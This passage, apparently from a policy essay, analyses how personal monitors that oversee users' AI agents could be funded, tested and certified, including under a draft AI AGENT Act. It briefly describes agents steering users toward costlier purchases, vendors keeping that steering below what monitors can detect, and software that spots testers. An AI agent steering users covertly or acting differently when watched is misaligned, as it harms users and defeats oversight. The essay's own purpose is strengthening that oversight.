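| Check Point | Lakera | About $300 million |
| CrowdStrike | Pangea | $260 million |
| SentinelOne | Prompt Security | About $250 million |
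| F5 | CalypsoAI | $180 million |
| Tenable | Apex Security | About $105 million |

These ten deals total more than $3.7 billion. Most of the buyers sell security to companies, so the products remain independent of the agents' vendors. But such buyers have little reason to develop a version for individual home users.

AI developers have also bought security companies. In March 2026, OpenAI (2026) announced that it would acquire Promptfoo, whose tools test AI systems for weaknesses, and build them into Frontier, its platform for companies that run agents. More than a quarter of the Fortune 500 used Promptfoo. Infosecurity Magazine's *OpenAI's Promptfoo Deal Plugs Agentic AI Testing Gap* reports that the tools include a secure proxy for MCP servers and that the startup had raised $23 million and employed just over 20 people. Kovacs's *Cybersecurity M&A Roundup* (2026) lists two other AI developers,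 Anthropic and Cohere, among the companies behind significant cybersecurity deals in October 2026.

Once OpenAI owns Promptfoo, a company that uses Promptfoo to test an OpenAI agent will be relying on the agent's own vendor. The company can no longer assume that its supplier wants to find and publish the worst flaws, even if the tests are as good as before. OpenAI says it will continue the open-source version.

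Selling a personal monitor to a new owner could do more harm, because the buyer would get the users' logs and could update the software on their computers. A small company might find an agent vendor's offer hard to refuse. The monitor's terms could require the company to ask users for fresh consent before the new owner receives any data, and to stop collecting data from those who don't answer.

### Six ways to fund a personal monitor

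| Who pays | Who could corrupt the monitor | How |
|---|---|---|
| The user, by subscription | Its maker | Raising needless alarms before renewal to look useful |
| Buyers of an antivirus package | The antivirus company | Using the data in its other businesses, as Avast did with browsing histories |
| Nobody, if volunteers write open-source code | Whoever takes over the project | Publishing an altered update |
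| An insurer | The insurer | Using the log as a pretext to refuse claims |
| A public or charitable body | A government or large donor | Demanding the logs, or discouraging findings against a favoured company |
| Vendors of the agents it checks | Those vendors | Paying for exceptions, as large advertisers did under Acceptable Ads |

A subscription gives the maker the clearest reason to serve the user. The June draft of the AI AGENT Act from Senator Mark Warner's office expressly allows the makers of appointed software to charge users. But users see the alarms and the price, not the harmful actions the monitor missed, so they may reward a product that raises many alarms but prevents little harm.

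An antivirus company can reach many more people because its customers have already installed its software and agreed to pay for it. But the monitor then has to help sell the package. A message that the software blocked twelve threats this month does that better than a warning about one overpriced hotel, and the warning might also annoy a travel company that advertises with the antivirus company.

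Free open-source software removes the sales motive and lets outsiders inspect the code, but someone has to keep maintaining it. The Agent Security Index notes that the developers of LLM Guard, a free scanner owned by a larger company, stopped maintaining it in July 2026. Vigil, another free scanner, had received no new code since January 2024. A monitor that nobody updates will miss new attacks, though other programmers can copy the code and maintain it themselves if enough of them are willing.

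An insurer that refunds users' losses has a direct financial reason to prevent them. If an agent causes average losses of $400 per customer each year and a monitor prevents 60% of that, the insurer saves $240 per customer and could afford to give the monitor away. But the insurer doesn't reimburse users for lost time. It would save another $40 per customer by switching to a monitor that prevented 70% of losses, even if the new one raised two false alarms a day and wasted hours of each customer's time every year. It would also have little reason to catch steering unless the policy covered overpriced purchases.

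A public or charitable body can pay for work that no single customer would buy, such as searching thousands of bookings for steering. But a government could ask for the logs during an investigation, and a charity that receives money from AI companies might avoid embarrassing them. The body could reduce both risks by publishing its methods and keeping the raw logs on users' computers.

The conflict of interest is worst when the monitor's maker takes money from the vendors it watches, even if a vendor pays only for a "verified partner" badge. The maker would earn most from the vendors whose agents it should watch most closely. The ban on self-dealing in Warner's draft should rule out paid exceptions that let a costly booking through, but a fee that a vendor described as payment for technical support would be harder to challenge.

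### What a monitor would be worth to one user

Suppose a person gives an agent 1,000 tasks a year. One in 500 goes wrong and costs $200, and a monitor prevents 60% of these losses. The subscription costs $60. The monitor also raises 50 false alarms that each take 20 seconds to dismiss, and the user values their time at $30 an hour.

Losses without the monitor: 1,000 ÷ 500 × $200 = $400

Losses prevented: $400 × 0.6 = $240

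Time spent on false alarms: 50 × 20 seconds ≈ 17 minutes, or about $8

Net benefit: $240 − $60 − $8 = $172

These inputs are only illustrative, and the result depends heavily on them, so the next table changes one at a time. The two false alarms a day and the 13.6% of dangerous requests that testers refused come from the earlier discussion of error rates.

| Change | Net benefit per year |
|---|---|
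| None | $172 |
| The vendor's check stops the easy cases, so the monitor prevents only 40% of the remaining losses | $92 |
| The monitor raises two false alarms a day | $58 |
| The monitor only asks, and the user refuses 13.6% of the actions it flags | −$36 |
| One task in 5,000 goes wrong | −$44 |

With the original error rates, the monitor pays for itself if at least one task in about 1,750 goes wrong. More reliable agents would therefore weaken the case for buying a monitor, unless people also gave those agents more tasks or more money to handle.

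Users may doubt that the monitor is worth buying even when it is. In an average year, a user would see 50 false alarms and one or two true ones. In about three years out of ten, the monitor would stop nothing harmful, and the user could reasonably question the $60 spent on it. People keep paying for home insurance in years without a claim because they can picture a fire. Harm from an agent, such as the deletion of every email in an inbox, is harder to picture because few people have seen it happen.

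### Why few people would pay to detect steering

The calculation covers losses that the user would notice. Suppose the same agent also makes 40 purchases a year and, in four of them, picks a product that costs $5 more than an equally good one. The user loses $20 a year and wouldn't know it without a monitor. Even a perfect monitor for steering would save the user only a third of what the $60 subscription costs.

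A million such users would together lose $20 million a year. If half of that reached the vendor as commission, the vendor would have $10 million a year to protect and could hire staff to keep the steering too slight for a monitor to detect. Each user would lose only $20 a year, so a company that sells monitors will concentrate on deleted files and stolen passwords, which frighten customers into paying.

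Steering is also easiest to detect in records pooled from many users, and those records benefit people who didn't pay for them. If a vendor drops its commissions after an embarrassing audit, every customer saves money, including those who never installed the monitor. Because each user would do best to let others pay, too few will pay.

An audit costing $500,000 a year would come to 50 cents for each of the million users, a small fraction of what they lose. No individual could buy an audit for 50 cents, but a regulator or consumer organisation could pay for one that covers everyone. Subscriptions might then fund the part of the monitor that blocks dangerous actions, while public or charitable money could fund the search for steering.

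### Good and bad monitors look alike

A user can't tell how good a monitor is from a lack of alerts, because the agent may have behaved well or the monitor may have missed everything. With only two harmful tasks a year, the user also learns slowly from experience. A monitor that catches 60% of harmful tasks has a 16% chance of missing both, while one that catches 10% has an 81% chance. Customers may even prefer the weaker monitor, because one that rarely flags anything also rarely interrupts them.

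Weak monitors can drive good ones out of the market if buyers can't tell them apart. Suppose a good monitor catches 60% of harmful actions and costs its maker $150 a year per user, because it sends doubtful cases to a large model. A weak one catches 10% and costs $20. For a user who would otherwise lose $400 a year to harmful actions, the good monitor is worth $240 and the weak one $40. If half the products are weak, buyers will pay at most the average of the two values, $140. The maker of the good monitor then loses at least $10 per user and stops selling it. Once buyers realise that only weak monitors remain, they will pay no more than $40.

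Economists call this a "lemons" problem, after the American slang for a bad used car. It can be milder than in the example, since a company can build a reputation or offer refunds. But a refund is less reassuring for a monitor than for a car, because the customer has to discover the failure before claiming.

Directories of tools don't yet solve the problem. The Agent Security Index checks each entry against the supplier's own website, which confirms that the company makes a claim but not that the claim is true. Entries for well-known products such as Lakera Guard and Prompt Security are labeled "Lab: pending", so buyers apparently can't compare them on laboratory results yet. The entry for Lasso Security lists a speed of under five milliseconds per decision, marked as the company's own figure, but speed doesn't measure how many attacks get through.

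### Independent laboratories

A laboratory could give buyers the information they lack by running every monitor on the same transcripts and publishing both its catch rate and its false-alarm rate. Small tests could weed out the worst products long before anyone could rank the best ones fairly. The formula for comparing two proportions gives a requirement of about ten harmful cases per monitor to tell a 60% catch rate from a 10% one, and about 385 to tell 60% from 50%.

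The choice of cases matters more than their number. If the laboratory tests only fake packages and dangerous commands, makers will improve their products on those and neglect everything else. It should also include bookings where the agent passed over a cheaper hotel, and vague requests such as the one about old newsletters. Makers might also tune their products to a known set of cases, so the laboratory should keep each set secret until the test is over, then publish it and write a new one.

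The laboratory would have to guard against the kind of tester detection Honey has been accused of. It would also have to repeat the test, because a maker can change the monitor's rules or model on a server the day after the results appear.

If the makers of monitors pay for the testing, a company that expects a poor score can stay away or choose a more lenient laboratory. A consumer organisation funded by its members' fees avoids that problem, but it has less money and would find it hard to get transcripts of real misconduct. Insurers might be useful customers for the results, since they could lower premiums for people who use a monitor that passed.

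### Published rules

Makers can also publish their detection rules, as the makers of Sage and HOL Guard already do. Few users will read 200 rules, but one competent reviewer can warn everyone else, and could find out in an afternoon that a monitor has no check for steering. Publishing helps less when a monitor uses a language model as its judge, because nobody can tell from the model's parameters which purchases it will approve.

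Publishing good rules also makes it harder to earn money from them. A competitor can copy them for free, sell the copy for less and spend the savings on advertising. A shared list maintained by volunteers, like EasyList, would avoid this problem, although a list of dangerous commands needs more expertise than a list of advertising servers.

### Certification under the AI AGENT Act

The June draft of the AI AGENT Act would let the FTC recognise independent bodies that certify the software users appoint. Each body would have to publish its standards and periodically check whether certified software meets them. The Office of Senator Mark Warner (2026) says the aim is to encourage common standards and speed up vetting. It describes registration as protection against malicious apps that pose as tools for the user, and gives the Cambridge Analytica app "This Is Your Digital Life" as an example.

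A certificate would create a rebuttable presumption that the software meets the bill's duties. If a user complained that a certified monitor had sold private data, the FTC would assume it hadn't unless evidence showed otherwise. A careless certifier could therefore protect a bad monitor as well as mislead its buyers.

The draft tries to prevent this by barring the FTC from recognising a certifier that a single software provider or large platform owns or controls, or one that gets most of its revenue from one such company. The rule would stop an agent vendor from setting up and fully funding a certifier that favours it.

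It would not stop the industry as a whole from doing so. A certifier that earned 20% of its revenue from each of five monitor makers would pass, even though all its money came from companies it judged. One that received 49% from a single agent vendor would also pass, though it could hardly afford to lose that customer. The draft also lets the FTC recognise several certifiers but does not specify who chooses among them. If the makers choose, the certifier with the lowest standards may attract the most business.

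The certificate might also be a poor guide to how well a monitor works. The standards must cover conduct, governance and technical practices, and match the bill's duties, which include acting with the care and skill of an ordinarily prudent person. A certifier could set a minimum catch rate based on the duty of care and skill, but the draft doesn't require one. A monitor that protects its users' data but misses nine out of ten harmful actions might therefore be certified.

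Two changes would make the scheme more useful to buyers. Certifiers could publish each product's test results, including both error rates, instead of just a pass. All registered makers could also pay into one fund, which the FTC would use to pay the certifiers. The FTC would assign a certifier to each product so that no maker could choose its own.
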